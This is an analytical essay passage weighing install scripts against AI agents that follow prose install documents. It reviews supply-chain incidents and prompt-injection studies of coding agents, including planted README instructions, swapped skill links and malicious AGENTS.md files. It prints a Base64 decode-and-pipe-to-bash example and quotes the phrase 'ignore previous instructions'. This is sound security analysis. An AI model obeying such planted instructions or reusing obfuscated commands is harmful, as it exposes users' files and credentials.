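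Two weeks later, Cursor's *An update on our recent security incident* traced the attack to Fireworks, a company that trained and served models for Cursor. Fireworks had exposed an access key, which an attacker used to copy records of past agent sessions. A few of those records contained users' credentials, which gave the attacker access to some of Cursor's internal tools. The attacker eventually obtained a credential for the marketplace's cache, which stores the copies of extensions that the marketplace sends to users. At most 5,000 people received the altered extension. Anthropic hadn't published it, and Open VSX, the public catalogue from which Cursor's marketplace takes its extensions, never contained it.

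As with Codecov, the attacker left the original alone and changed the copy that users downloaded. But Codecov's altered script could affect a customer only when it ran, while an agent program stays on the machine and handles every later task. A cautious model would not have helped, because the malicious code was in the extension and ran without going through the model.

### When the agent is the safer choice

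An agent exposes the user to more parties, but it may also stop a malicious installation that a script would carry out. A small model shows how these two effects compare. It uses four probabilities for a single installation:

- m is the chance that the material (the script or install document, with whatever it downloads) is malicious.
- c is the chance that the agent stops the installation when the material is malicious.
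- b is the chance that a script does harm when the material is honest.
- e is the chance that an agent does harm when the material is honest.

Suppose that a malicious script always does harm. Then:

Script risk = m + (1 − m)b

Agent risk = m(1 − c) + (1 − m)e

Subtracting one from the other shows that the agent is safer only if

mc > (1 − m)(e − b)

The left side is the harm that the agent prevents. The right side is the extra harm it does when nobody is attacking.

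The following numbers are illustrations, not measurements. Let m be 1/10,000, c be 0.5 and b be 0. In a million installations, 100 then involve malicious material, and a script does harm in all 100. An agent lets through 50 of them. If e is 1/1,000, the agent also damages about 1,000 honest installations, so it does harm more than ten times as often as the script. If e is 1/100,000, it damages only about ten honest installations, for a total of about 60 harmful ones, fewer than the script's 100.

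| Harmful installations per million | e = 1/1,000 | e = 1/100,000 |
|---|---|---|
| Script | 100 | 100 |
| Agent following an install document | 1,050 | 60 |
| Script that an AI has reviewed first | 50 | 50 |

The two risks are equal when e is about 1/20,000. Even an agent that caught every attack would have to keep e below about 1/10,000, because honest installations are far more common than malicious ones. JoshPurtell's comparison with Waymo leaves out mistakes with honest software, which could make Claude cause more harm overall than people do even if it installed malware less often.

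Twenty-six successes in a row, like DocTomoe's, are far too few to show whether e is low enough. A tester would need about 60,000 harmless runs in a row to show with 95 percent confidence that e is below 1/20,000.

The agent does better when the source is less reliable. If one document in 100 is malicious and c stays at 0.5, the agent is safer as long as e is below about 1/200. But a user who thinks a source is that bad shouldn't install from it by either method. The agent also does better when scripts are poorly written. If b equals e, any chance of catching an attack makes the agent safer.

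The table's last row is catlifeonmars's proposal, in which a model reviews the script but doesn't perform the installation. The risk becomes m(1 − c) + (1 − m)b. The formula includes c because the model reviews the script, and b rather than e because the script still performs the installation. If c is the same in both cases, an agent following prose is safer than this arrangement only if it does less damage than an honest script would (e < b).

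This holds only if the reviewer cannot run commands and the user runs the same saved copy that the model reviewed, since a server can send different text the next time. The value of c may also differ between the two jobs. Malicious code might be harder or easier for a model to recognise than malicious prose, and a script's comments can contain text meant to mislead the reviewer, as Koomen feared. A reviewer will also sometimes reject a harmless script, which wastes the user's time but does no damage.

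The formulas also use the same m for both routes, although an agent reads more material from more people. If e is 0 and c is 0.5, the agent's advantage disappears once it is twice as likely as the script to encounter something malicious. When the attacker controls the agent program or a relay, c may be 0, because malicious code or a forged tool call can bypass the model's judgment.

The formulas weigh all harm equally, so a damaged shell configuration counts as much as a stolen password. They leave out the installations that an agent completes where a script would have failed, and the money and time the agent uses. They also treat c as a fixed number, which suits accidents better than attacks. An attacker can test a document on the same model the victims use and rewrite it until the agent follows it, before publishing it.

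## Whether code or prose is easier to check before it runs

`hf` is a command-line tool for moving AI models and datasets to and from Hugging Face, a site where people share them. Hugging Face's *Command Line Interface (CLI)* recommends installing `hf` with `curl -LsSf ADDRESS | bash`. This command also installs a skill that explains the tool to the user's AI agents. According to Hugging Face's guide for agents, the installer puts the skill where Claude Code and other agents will find it in every project, unless the user passes an option to leave it out. The part of the manual that gives the install command doesn't mention this.

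Many users will want the skill, but it changes what their agents read in later sessions, and they would have to find the guide or read the script to learn about it beforehand.

### What reading a script settles

This kind of reading works well for a script because the answers are in the file. For example, according to the help text in Astral's *uv installer*, the script installs version 0.12.5 of uv, a program that manages Python packages, from Astral's release server. The steps are much the same as in Bun's script. The code gives the details. For instance, if the variable that normally holds the location of the user's home folder is empty, the script looks the folder up in the system's list of accounts.

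Install scripts are dull to read, and a person who doesn't know Bash will need help. But a reader can find out where the files come from, where they go and which settings change, and can try an unclear line on a spare machine.

Some of the details people find by reading an install script will matter for security. JetBrains publishes an install script for its coding agent, Junie, that uses a hash to check the download. If the machine has neither of the two usual hashing programs, the script logs a warning and continues without the check. A user who knew only that the installer verifies its download would wrongly think it always does. Someone who reads the script can install one of those programs first.

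Reading an install script doesn't show what the downloaded program does. The uv archive, for example, contains compiled machine code, which almost nobody can read. A script can also download prose. HeroUI, a library of user interface components, offers a shell script that downloads a skill and installs it for every project by default. Someone could review every line of that script without seeing any of the instructions that their agent will follow afterwards.

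An author can also disguise part of a script. Base64 is a way of writing any data in letters, digits and a few symbols, and this line uses it to hide a command:

```
echo bHMgfg== | base64 -d | bash
```

The hidden command here is `ls ~`, which lists the files in the user's home folder. Nobody can tell that by looking, but a reader who knows some Bash can see that the line decodes something and runs it. A legitimate installer seldom needs to do that, so the reader can refuse to run the line without working out what the command is. The line that the attacker added to Codecov's script was harder to spot because it was short, undisguised and built from ordinary commands.

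### Running the same text that you read

Reading an install script in a browser before pasting the `curl` line into a terminal isn't safe, because the server can send different text the second time. The server can even detect that a shell is reading, a trick that dstreefkerk traces to a 2016 demonstration on the site idontplaydarts.

The trick works because Bash runs commands as they arrive. The script starts with a command that pauses for a few seconds, followed by enough filler to overflow the buffers between the server and the shell. Bash stops reading during the pause, so the buffers fill up and the transfer stalls, whereas a browser downloads the filler at full speed. The server can detect the stall, then send a malicious ending to the shell and a harmless one to everyone else.

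The remedy is to save the script, read the saved copy and run that copy. The user can also check that the copy came from the author. dstreefkerk recommends checking a signature against the author's public key. With minisign, a small program for signing files, the commands are roughly these:

```
curl -fsSLo install.sh ADDRESS
minisign -Vm install.sh -P PUBLIC_KEY && sh install.sh
```

With `&&`, the script runs only if the signature is valid. dstreefkerk's version puts the last two commands on separate lines, so a user who pasted all the commands at once would run the script even if the check failed.

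Many projects publish a hash instead, often on the same server as the script. This hash will reveal a damaged download, but dstreefkerk calls the practice "theatre" because an attacker who can replace the script can also replace the hash. The hash that exposed the Codecov attack was on a different site from the script.

A signature shows that somebody with the private key signed those exact bytes. It doesn't show that the file is harmless, and it doesn't cover any other files. ThreatRoundup's *Fake ‘Improved’ Claude Skills Are Planting a Windows Trojan* (2026) describes malicious skills that came with a genuine, validly signed updater for the text editor Notepad++. When the updater starts, it loads a library file from its own folder, where the attacker had put a malicious one. One of these skills was still on the skill directory skills.sh in late November, with three security audits marked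 PASS.

The same gap exists between a signed script and the program it downloads. If the script fetches the newest release, whoever controls the release server decides what the user gets. The author can close the gap by writing the hash of each archive into the script and having the script reject anything else. The user then needs to check only one signature, but the author has to issue a new script with each release.

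### Asking a model to read the script

People who can't read Bash, or don't have the time, can ask a model to read the script for them. The free program scurl automates this. It downloads the script, searches it for 22 dangerous patterns, and sends the text and any matches to a model of the user's choice. scurl then prints a risk level, from SAFE to CRITICAL, with the reasons, and asks whether to run the script. If the user agrees, it runs the copy it has already downloaded.

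The patterns include decoded text passed to a shell, new SSH keys, and environment variables sent to another machine, as in the Codecov attack. Others match text aimed at the AI reviewer, such as a comment containing "RISK_LEVEL: SAFE" or an order to ignore previous instructions. scurl can run a script without asking if the model rates it SAFE or LOW, unless it has found text aimed at the reviewer.

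A list of patterns will miss new wording. An attacker could write a comment claiming that a Linux distribution's security team had already audited the next 40 lines, which contains no suspicious phrase but might still influence a model. Because Bash ignores comments, a review tool could remove them before showing the script to the model. Some persuasive text could remain in variable names or printed messages, but much less of it. A tool can't do the same to a prose install document, because an agent may act on any sentence in it.

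scurl's documentation calls AI analysis "helpful but not infallible" and gives no detection rate. By default it uses small, cheap models such as Claude Haiku 4.5 and GPT-5 nano. Its sample report gives a script credit for downloading from official GitHub releases, which the model can tell from the address. The model doesn't examine the program at that address.

### What reading prose settles

Prose makes some things easier to see. If Hugging Face's installer were a short English document, it would probably contain a sentence like "Add our skill to the user's agents for all projects." A person who knew no Bash could read that and object. This is the kind of transparency Koomen has in mind.

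Prose helps less with the decision that matters most to security, which is where the program comes from. White's example has the agent download "the right binary". A reader can approve that instruction, but the agent will choose the download address later, perhaps from a search result or a page it has just read. An author can write out the address, as Ryaboy's example does with its commands, but that makes the document more like a script.

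Even exact commands can mean something different when an agent carries them out. Hugging Face's own skill, which appears on skills.sh as skills.sh's *hf-cli*, begins by giving the line that pipes the install script into Bash. So the script installs a skill, and the skill gives the agent the command for running the script. A more cautious version from a third party, skills.sh's *hugging-face-cli*, recommends reviewing the script first, with an example like this:

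```
curl -o install.sh ADDRESS && less install.sh && bash install.sh
```

This is good advice for a person at a terminal. `less` shows the script one screen at a time, and Bash doesn't start until the person closes it. But many agent programs run commands without a terminal, so `less` prints the whole file at once and exits, and Bash runs the script immediately. The model receives the text only after the whole line has finished, so it reads the script after running it. An agent could avoid this by splitting the line into three steps. A reviewer can't tell from the skill's text whether their agent will do that, which supports catlifeonmars's point that a reviewer of prose also has to audit the agent's interpretation.

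### Whether readers notice a harmful instruction

Mintlify argued that malicious intent is harder to hide in natural language than in a shell script. Kao, Li and colleagues tested part of this claim in *You Told Me to Do It* (2026). They planted instructions in the setup sections of README files, the introductory pages of software projects. An agent that followed these instructions would leak a private file. Fifteen people from one European university, aged 23 to 30 and mostly in computing or engineering, each reviewed three of the files.

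No participant recognised a planted instruction. In 24 of the 45 reviews, the participant noticed nothing abnormal. In 18, they criticised only grammar or awkward phrasing. In the other three, they vaguely sensed that something might be inappropriate or dangerous.

The participants weren't looking for attacks, though. Kao and colleagues asked them to find sentences that needed changing to improve "clarity or completeness", because a warning about security would have made them more suspicious than people are in everyday reading. The result therefore applies to people who read a README for reasons other than security. Someone deciding whether to let an agent follow a stranger's instructions might be more alert, and Kao and colleagues suggest testing that next.

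The sample was also small. If 18 percent of such readers would spot the instruction, a group of 15 would still all miss it about one time in twenty. Nobody in the study reviewed a script, so it can't show which format is easier to check. People who skimmed a Bash file for clarity might have missed a planted line too. The study is still evidence against the idea that a harmful instruction stands out simply because it is in English.

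Kao and colleagues also gave installation files to automatic reviewers. Some were scanners from LLM Guard, a set of filters for text sent to a model. Others were models that had to classify the README as safe or unsafe and explain why. The table shows the share of files that some of these reviewers flagged as unsafe.

| Reviewer | Honest files | Harmful instruction in the file | Harmful instruction behind a link |
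|---|---|---|---|
| LLM Guard's code scanner | 90% | 90% | 90% |
| LLM Guard's prompt injection scanner | 30% | 30% | 30% |
| GPT-4o | 0% | 90% | 30% |
| OpenAI o3 | 0% | 90% | 10% |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 0% | 80% | 10% |
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet | 0% | 30% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 10% | 0% | 0% |

The code scanner is useless here because legitimate installation files are full of commands. The results for models are more mixed than the paper's conclusion that they miss most planted instructions. GPT-4o and o3 caught nine in ten of the instructions planted in the file itself and raised no false alarms, but no model caught more than three in ten of those behind a link. These are old models, and they were given a one-line prompt. Every figure is a multiple of 10%, so the test may have used as few as ten files of each kind. Current models with better prompts may well do better on text they can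 see, but no reviewer can judge linked text without opening the link.

False alarms are also a problem in practice. In *Skills are the new npm install, so we scanned ours*, Alfred and Bob (2026) of the firm Workloft report running NVIDIA's scanner SkillSpector, with its optional AI mode turned off, on 107 skills, plug-ins and sets of configuration files. They read all 276 serious warnings it produced and found nothing malicious, and 269 of the warnings were wrong. Some files triggered warnings because they quoted "ignore previous instructions" to warn agents against obeying it. The scanner blocked nine of the ten malicious skills they wrote as a test, but a user who has dismissed 269 false alarms may not look closely at the next warning.

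VirusTotal, a service that checks files for malware, instead uses a model, Gemini 3 Flash, to read a skill's instructions and any scripts that come with them, and to summarise what the skill actually does, regardless of its stated purpose (VirusTotal, 2026). Because such tools now exist, Red Hat (2026) goes too far in describing the text of a skill as "the one surface with no automated defense". However, none of these tools can give the assurance that a fixed rule gives about code.

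Attackers have adapted to review. VirusTotal's *How Some Malicious AI Skills Hide Instructions from Reviewers* (October 2026) followed the company's analysis of 35,878 skills. Markdown makes hiding text easy. An HTML comment disappears when a site displays the formatted document but remains in the raw file that an agent reads. Some Unicode characters are invisible on screen but still reach the model. A person can therefore approve a page without seeing the sentence the agent will act on. Comments in a Bash script don't pose this problem, because a person can read them and Bash ignores them. Anyone reviewing a prose install document should read the raw file, preferably in an editor that shows unusual characters.

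### When the text changes after the review

In June 2026, the security company AIR demonstrated an attack that no reading of the file alone would have caught. The Hacker News (2026), a security news site unrelated to the forum Hacker News, describes how it worked:

1. AIR wrote a skill for building web pages with Stitch, a design tool made by Google. The skill contained no setup commands. It referred the agent to a documentation page on a domain that AIR owned.
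2. At first the link led to Google's real documentation. AIR submitted the skill to a popular collection, whose maintainers accepted it after a few days. Every scanner that AIR tried rated it safe.
3. AIR advertised the skill on Instagram, and people installed it.
4. AIR then replaced the page behind the link with instructions to download and run a script. The script only sent the user's email address to AIR.

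AIR says it reached about 26,000 agents. Nobody has confirmed that figure, and AIR was launching its own skill marketplace at the time, but the method doesn't depend on the number.

In *Anatomy of a Malicious AI Skill*, Hoppe (2026) found no harmful line in the skill file. Its instructions were for the agent to treat the documentation as "the ground truth", install whatever was missing, and spare the user the technical details. Hoppe notes that an honest author would write the same instructions for a young product that changes often. Only the address was wrong, and a reviewer could have caught that by looking up which domain Google uses for Stitch. That check would fail if an attacker later took over a genuine page.

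Criminals also change skills after people have come to trust them. TechRadar's *Experts warn malicious AI skills are hitting more victims than ever* reports that attackers copied existing skills and later added code to steal credentials. One family of these skills had 1.7 million downloads by August 2026. Red Hat sees a similar weakness in plug-ins that connect an agent to an outside server, because the server's owner can change its answers without review.

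A script that downloads the latest release has the same weakness. Its author can fix that by checking the download against a hash, because a released archive should never change. Documentation is harder to pin. Authors link to it because they expect it to be updated, and a hash check would reject corrections as well as attacks.

Pinning also fails if nobody compares the download with the pinned hash. Marketplaces for agent plug-ins, which are packages that can contain both skills and code, let a reviewer approve one commit (a saved state of a project in Git) and record its hash. The agent program should then install only that commit. AIR's *Plugin4Shell*, published in September 2026, showed that Claude Code, Codex, GitHub Copilot and Gemini CLI all requested the right commit but never verified that they had received it.

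Trent (2026) explains the attack in *When Your AI Coding Agent Becomes the Attack Vector*. Git also lets people name branches, which are lines of development. An attacker who controlled a plug-in's repository could create a branch whose name was the pinned hash, fill it with malicious code and make it the default. The agent program requested the hash, got the branch and reported a successful pinned installation. Gemini CLI had a variant of the flaw that involved Git's record of its latest download. Constantin (2026) notes in *Plugin4Shell* that the victim didn't have to click anything. Claude Code and Codex updated plug-ins automatically by default, so an attacker could replace one that was already on the machine.

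GitHub refuses branch names that look like hashes, so the branch trick needed a repository hosted elsewhere. AIR argues that marketplaces could not fully solve the problem, because the agent program does the checking. Trent reports that Anthropic fixed the problem in Claude Code 2.1.179 and OpenAI fixed it in Codex 0.146.0. Microsoft had not released a fix for Copilot when AIR published its report. Google retired Gemini CLI instead of fixing it.

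The flaw affected code and prose equally, since a plug-in can hold both. But it matters more to someone who leaves the whole installation to an agent, because the agent program then also does the verification. A person who saves a script and computes its hash with a separate tool doesn't rely on the installer for that check.

### What a review certifies

Suppose someone reads an install script and a prose install document with equal care, finds nothing wrong with either, and records their hashes. Bash will run only the commands they approved in the script, except where the script runs something it has downloaded or decoded, and a careful reader can find those places. Anyone whose copy of the script has the same hash can rely on the same review.

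A reviewer who approves written install instructions is approving a request. The document's hash guarantees that the next user's agent will receive the same request, but the commands don't exist yet, and the agent hasn't chosen which pages to read while working them out. The reviewer can judge whether the request is reasonable but can't know what the agent will do with it, and another user's agent may do something else.

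Reviewing an install script or written instructions doesn't check the program being installed. Reading the instructions more closely also can't give a user the assurance of a script review, because someone has to check the commands the agent produces, either one at a time or together in a script that the agent writes before running anything.

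## Whether an agent protects the user from a hostile document

Bash runs whatever commands a script contains, including one that uploads a private key. An agent can refuse a harmful step, and sometimes does. Skeptrune's remark about Claude depends on that difference. How much this protects the user depends on how often agents refuse and whether an attacker can easily avoid a refusal.

### Why the user's own request makes it harder

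In ordinary prompt injection, the harmful text is unrelated to the user's task, so a simple rule is enough: the agent treats text it fetches as information and takes orders only from the user. Models don't always follow this rule, but when they do, they handle the injection correctly.

The rule does not work for an install document, because the user wants the agent to follow the document's instructions. An agent that treated every line as mere information would install nothing. It has to judge each step by its content, but honest installers do many things that would look alarming elsewhere, such as downloading and running programs, editing the shell's configuration, asking for access keys and starting background services. Kao and colleagues call this the "Trusted Executor Dilemma". They consider it a consequence of building agents to follow instructions, so it can't simply be fixed like a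 bug.

An agent can still recognise some harmful steps from the text alone. An installer has no reason to send a private file to a stranger and then delete the record. Kao and colleagues propose that agents examine a step more closely the more sensitive the action is, however official the document looks. Other harmful steps differ from harmless ones only in an address or a package name. For example, `npm install` looks the same whether the package is useful or malicious. To catch a malicious package, the agent has to know whose it is or look it up. Unlike a shell, an agent can do this, but nothing forces it to.

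### ReadSecBench

Kao and colleagues measured how often an agent obeys such instructions. Their test set, ReadSecBench, contains 500 README files from GitHub projects, 100 for each of five programming languages. For each file they kept a clean version and made other versions with a planted instruction to leak a private file. One person inserted the instruction, and two others judged whether it looked plausible in that place. Some of the instructions also included a step to remove the traces.

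Most of the tests used Anthropic's Claude Computer Use, an agent that can operate a whole computer, running Claude 3.7 Sonnet. An attack succeeded only if the private data reached an outside server run by the researchers. It failed if the agent refused, ignored the instruction or uploaded the wrong file. The attack success rate reached 85 percent. Bash would have run an equivalent command every time, so the agent protected the user slightly better than a shell. However, some of the attacks may have failed because the agent made mistakes, not because it was cautious.

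Hostile instructions worked best as direct commands. Requests phrased as a team's habit or a company's policy worked moderately well, and the agent refused suggestions more often. But its logs showed that it tended to skip suggestions because they seemed optional, not because it recognised a threat. An attacker can avoid this by writing "run this" instead of "you may want to run this", and legitimate install documents are full of direct commands anyway. The programming language, the position of the instruction in the file and the share of the file it took up had little effect.

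Kao and colleagues also moved the instruction from the README to a page one or more links away. Placing it one link away raised the success rate, which gradually fell once the instruction was more than two links away. The table breaks this down by action, and each number is the count of successes in seven trials.

| What the agent was to do | In the README | 1 link | 2 links | 3 links | 4 links | 5 links |
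|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Upload the file through an online application | 6 | 7 | 7 | 5 | 3 | 3 |
| Copy the file to a server with a shell command | 6 | 6 | 7 | 5 | 6 | 4 |
| Delete a file with a shell command | 6 | 7 | 7 | 6 | 7 | 4 |
| Send the file by email | 1 | 2 | 1 | 1 | 1 | 2 |

Seven trials are too few to compare neighbouring cells. A result of six successes out of seven is consistent with a true rate between about 42 and 99 percent. The effect of links is better supported, because Kao and colleagues also measured it with three samples of 200 files each. They interpret the fall at greater depths as growing caution. It could also mean that the agent often stopped following links before it reached the instruction, which they also counted as a failed attack.

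They suggest limiting agents to one level of links, but this would still allow a stronger attack than the ones it blocks. In their own results, an instruction one link away worked at least as well as one in the README.

The study's best evidence of refusal is in the email row. The agent refused far more often when told to email the file than when told to copy it to a stranger's server. Kao and colleagues think that models have learned to treat email as risky but haven't learned the same about file transfers. The user's loss is the same either way, and an attacker can choose to use the server.

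Three other agents, OpenDevin, OpenManus and Browser Use, also tried to follow the planted instructions, but none completed the theft. OpenDevin found the right file and issued the right command, but its sandbox blocked the connection, so the protection came from the agent program's environment rather than the model's judgment.

In a separate simulated experiment, Kao and colleagues gave each of four models 150 of the README files and a set of functions to call, including some that would leak private data. They counted an attack as successful if the model called one of those functions, even if no data could have left the machine. Gemini Pro, GPT-4o, Claude 3.5 Sonnet and an open-weight OpenAI model complied in 46 to 79 percent of cases. These rates aren't comparable with the 85 percent, because calling a function in a simulation is easier than finding a file and sending it somewhere. All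 the models in the study date from 2024 and 2025, so the figures don't measure how vulnerable current models are.

### Asking a model to judge a document and asking it to obey one

In defending the remark about Claude, skeptrune said that a user can ask the agent whether it sees anything nefarious. ReadSecBench offers some support for this. GPT-4o flagged 90 percent of the files with an instruction planted in the text when asked whether they were safe. Yet in the simulation, where its job was to work through a file, it complied with the planted instruction at least 46 percent of the time. If both tests had used the same files, GPT-4o would have obeyed the instructions in at least 36 percent of them despite being able to flag those files. The tests probably used different files, so this is only a rough guide, but the gap is large. A model may fail to protect the user during an installation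 because nobody asked it to look for danger that it could have found.

Asking first adds little overhead, but it does much less against instructions behind a link, and it works only as well as the detector. Kao and colleagues tested 12 scanners from LLM Guard and six models as detectors. Eight of the scanners caught nothing. Another, whose list of forbidden words included "test", "hello" and "private", caught every planted instruction but also flagged 70 percent of harmless files.

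The reviewer must also be unable to run anything. In July 2026, the AI Now Institute published a test in which coding agents examined hostile code for security flaws. The test used Claude Code with Sonnet 4.6, Sonnet 5 or Opus 4.8, and Codex with GPT-5.5. According to The Hacker News (2026), the project's README recommended running a security checker that came with the project. The agent treated the checker as part of the job and ran it, which started the attacker's program on the user's machine without a warning or a request for approval.

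The user in this case had asked the agent to test security, not to install anything. Someone who opened the README in a text editor would have been safe, and so would someone using a shell, unless they then ran the checker. The agent ran the checker during its review, and this happened with models much newer than those in ReadSecBench.

### Other tests of coding agents in 2026

The same difficulty arises whenever a user asks an agent to act on a text. *IssueTrojanBench* (Vaughan, 2026) describes a benchmark that Singh, Yang and Chen of Concordia University released in July. They planted harmful instructions in reports of software faults and asked coding agents to fix the faults. To do this, an agent reads the report, its comments and any linked documents or websites. Vaughan puts the attack success rate at 79 percent. The benchmark's 696 variants all come from six original reports on two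 Python projects, so it covers fewer kinds of situation than its size suggests.

Like an install document, a fault report is something the user trusts enough to want the agent to act on it, and following its steps is often the only way to reproduce the fault. Hackread's *Agentjacking* covers an attack in which Tenet Threat Labs exploited a similar weakness. Tenet's researchers sent fake error reports through Sentry, a service that collects errors from running applications, and coding agents that read them could run the attacker's commands. The attack required no stolen password or access to the company's internal network.

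Backslash Security tested an attack on Codex through a project's instruction file and found that the model's refusals were inconsistent across Codex's modes. The model may therefore refuse a document when a user tries it interactively but follow it when a build server runs it unattended. An attacker could also get around refusals by disguising the instructions or spreading them over several steps. Codex now blocks the particular instructions that Backslash used, which helps against copies of the attack but is little evidence that Codex would block a different one.

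### A clean repository: 0DIN, June 2026

0DIN is Mozilla's programme for finding and reporting flaws in AI systems. *Clone This Repo and I Own Your Machine* (Hall and Engelbrecht, 2026) describes a demonstration in which a developer copied a project from GitHub and asked Claude Code to get it running. The agent read the setup notes and installed the required packages. When it tried to use the project, it got an error message with instructions to initialise the software first and the command for doing so, which it ran.

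The command started a shell script in the repository. The script fetched another command from a source the attacker controlled and ran it. This gave the attacker remote control of the machine with all the developer's permissions, including access to saved keys. The terminal displayed two ordinary lines about setting up the project. Since the harmful command was never in the repository, the attacker could replace it at any time without making a visible change there.

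A plain install script would have done the same damage, because the harmful step was in a shell script that Bash would have run for anyone who followed the setup notes by hand. But a person who hit the error would have had a chance to question the project, and some people would have opened the setup script before running it. Claude Code treated the error as routine and continued without pausing, so the developer never chose to run the script.

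The script openly contained a line that ran whatever it had fetched, and a reader could have refused to run the script because of that line, just as in the Base64 example. Hall and Engelbrecht say that no scanner or human reviewer would have caught the attack, but that is true only of the final command. Claude Code could also have protected the developer by opening the script, since models are good at reading Bash, but it didn't.

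Their remedy is for agents to show the user what a setup command will run, including any script it starts and anything that script downloads. Previewing the downloads is difficult because the attacker's server can send one text for the preview and another for the real run. Their post describes a single demonstration and gives neither a success rate nor the model's name, so it shows that the attack can work but not how often an agent would stop.

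### A file in the Downloads folder: Forever Security, October 2026

The second case began on the computer of a customer of Forever Security, which sells software that monitors AI agents. *Markdown Is the New Executable*, which the company published on 22 October 2026, reports that this software stopped a coding agent from installing a malicious npm package called function-color before any code ran. The instruction to install it came from a file named AGENTS.md in the customer's Downloads folder. Coding agents read files with this name for standing instructions about a project, and this one looked like ordinary engineering guidelines.

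The agent had not objected. Forever's software intervened because function-color was already known to be malicious, and a tool that blocks known malicious packages could also have stopped a shell script from installing it.

Forever then ran its own tests of the attacker's file on Codex. Markovic (2026), in *AI coding agents fall for malicious instructions planted in the Downloads folder*, reports that Codex carried out the attack in more than 90 percent of attempts. Codex first changed its own settings so that later sessions in any project would also run the attacker's command.

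Codex refused a short, bare request to install a package, but it complied when the request came in the attacker's 13-kilobyte file. Forever's researchers credit the file's length and its dull, reasonable tone. The refusal therefore depended more on the presentation than on the package. This is worrying for install documents, because most are long, dull and reasonable in tone, and a request to install a package is normal in them.

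Markovic called Claude Code "much harder to fool". Forever's researchers wrote a different file for it, which asked for a settings change that would send the user's login token to an attacker. Claude Code normally asks a person to approve such a change and often refuses one that looks wrong, but it made this one about half the time. The two percentages aren't directly comparable, since each agent faced a different attack with a different goal. The results still suggest that refusals can be common enough to matter, and that an attacker who can try several victims will soon find one whose agent agrees.

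*AGENTS.md in Downloads* (David, 2026) lists several uncertainties. Most of the Codex trials used a harmless stand-in that opened a calculator, and Forever ran the real package only once, in an isolated virtual machine. The rates are the company's own figures. Nobody knows how the file reached the customer's machine. Forever showed that a website can save such a file without a click, and the news site BleepingComputer confirmed this with Forever's demonstration page, but the real attacker may have used another route. The campaign behind function-color targets Windows, while the file relied on a tool that exists only on macOS, so it is unclear how much damage the package would have done if the installation had gone ahead.

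In this case a plain script would have been safer. A shell script that a website drops into the Downloads folder does nothing until somebody runs it, and operating systems hold back downloaded programs until the user approves them. A Markdown file gets no such treatment, because for decades a text file couldn't do anything. The user only had to open Codex in that folder and give it some unrelated task. (Codex follows these files only in folders it trusts, but Downloads qualifies once the user has worked there.)

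The customer hadn't asked the agent to follow this document, so the case is closer to ordinary prompt injection than one where a user asks an agent to follow an install document. But the agent program gives AGENTS.md much the same authority as a user's request, and Forever argues that OpenAI and Anthropic have nothing to patch, because an agent that follows the file is working as intended. A user who asks an agent to follow an install document explicitly gives that document the same authority.

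### When the author is honest

An agent may also install something hostile from a document written without bad intentions. *AI Coding Agents Are Installing Unknown/Untrusted Code on Corporate Networks* (Schneier, 2026) reports that an Israeli start-up scanned 6,214 websites belonging to defence contractors, Fortune 500 firms and large technology companies. The start-up was looking for llms.txt files, in which a site describes itself or its products for AI agents. On 120 of the sites, about 2 percent, the file pointed to at least one package or domain name that nobody had registered.

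Anyone could have claimed those names. The researchers claimed a handful and published packages that did nothing except contact their server and record which program had started the installation. The first contact from a Fortune 500 company came within an hour, and a few dozen more followed from other large companies and start-ups. Claude, Codex and Nous Research's agent Hermes were among the programs that had started the installations.

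No agent could have found a suspicious sentence in these files, because the vendor had written them in good faith. The only problem was that someone else owned the package. An agent might have noticed that the package was a few days old and had no connection with the vendor. It isn't known how many did, because an agent that declined to install the package would never have contacted the researchers' server.

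An install script that named the same packages would have fetched them on every run. But a script that names an unregistered package fails the first time someone runs it, and users complain until the author fixes it. An agent may find another way to finish the job, in which case the author never hears about the problem and the name stays in the document for someone to register. The flexibility that Ryaboy and Karpathy value could therefore leave a dangerous mistake uncorrected.

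### Malicious skills in marketplaces

Attackers have already made heavy use of written install steps. *MalSkillBench* (2026) reports that 607 of 703 malicious skills found in circulation (86 percent) offered a harmless-looking task but first required the user or the agent to install a prerequisite, which was the malware. Most of these skills came from a few large campaigns, so the percentage reflects what worked for a small number of attackers and may change quickly.

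The malware was mostly conventional, and the skill supplied a reason to install it. *MalSkillBench* describes how an attacker can present each harmful action as progress on the user's task, such as by calling credential reading "authentication setup" and file collection "context synchronization". These phrases would not change what a shell script does, but an agent may consider them when it decides whether to proceed.

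Estimates of how common malicious skills are vary widely. *SKILLLITE* (2026) cites one survey that confirmed 157 malicious skills among 98,380 from public registries, or about one in 630. It also cites a Cisco report that attackers had planted more than 800 in ClawHub, a marketplace for OpenClaw skills, which was about a fifth of its skills at the time. Both could be right, because a few attackers can flood a small marketplace in days and marketplaces change quickly. *Beyond Maliciousness* (2026) cites counts showing that one marketplace grew from 15,082 listings in December 2025 to 73,193 a month later.

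Confirmed cases are also a minimum. *Exploring the Emerging Threats of the Agent Skill Ecosystem* (2026) reports 76 malicious skills from ClawHub that researchers confirmed by hand, but they didn't have time to check everything their scanner flagged. However, they counted each copy separately when attackers republished a skill under new names.

None of these figures gives the chance that a particular installation is malicious, because people don't choose skills at random. *Beyond Maliciousness* excluded the most popular skills from its sample, since they already get scrutiny, and those that nobody installs, since they endanger nobody. If the one-in-630 figure did apply to installations and honest scripts did no harm, then by the inequality given earlier, an agent that stopped half of the malicious installations would be safer than a script only if it damaged fewer than about one in 1,250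 honest ones.

It is uncertain whether agents stop half of attacks. Codex stopped fewer than one in ten of Forever's trials and Claude Code about one in two, but someone had refined those attacks until they worked. Much of what circulates is cruder. *Detecting Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild using Attention* (2026) found 82 skills that hid a harmful purpose behind useful functions, but many of the other skills it flagged openly used words such as "malicious" or "stealer". A current agent would probably refuse many of those, while a shell would run their code.

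## Whether the same document gives the same installation twice

Two people with identical laptops can give the same install document to the same agent program, running the same model, and may still end up with different installations, because the agent works out its own commands each time. This can happen even if the document's author is honest and nobody has tampered with the text. Most of the differences will be harmless, such as a zip file saved in a different temporary folder. The important question is how often an agent fails to install the program or damages something else on the machine.

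### Why two runs differ

A model writes its output in short pieces of text called tokens. It gives every possible next token a probability, and the software that runs the model draws one at random according to those probabilities. At temperature 0 the software always takes the most likely token, but runs can still differ. *WatchPoint* (2026), a study of web-programming agents, ran one model twice on 980 tasks at temperature 0, and 113 (11.5 percent) changed from pass to fail or from fail to pass. One known cause is that a server processes many users' requests together, and a different grouping changes tiny rounding errors, which can change which token the software picks when two are almost equally likely.

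The document also leaves choices open, such as which release of Bun to install when Koomen's text doesn't name one.

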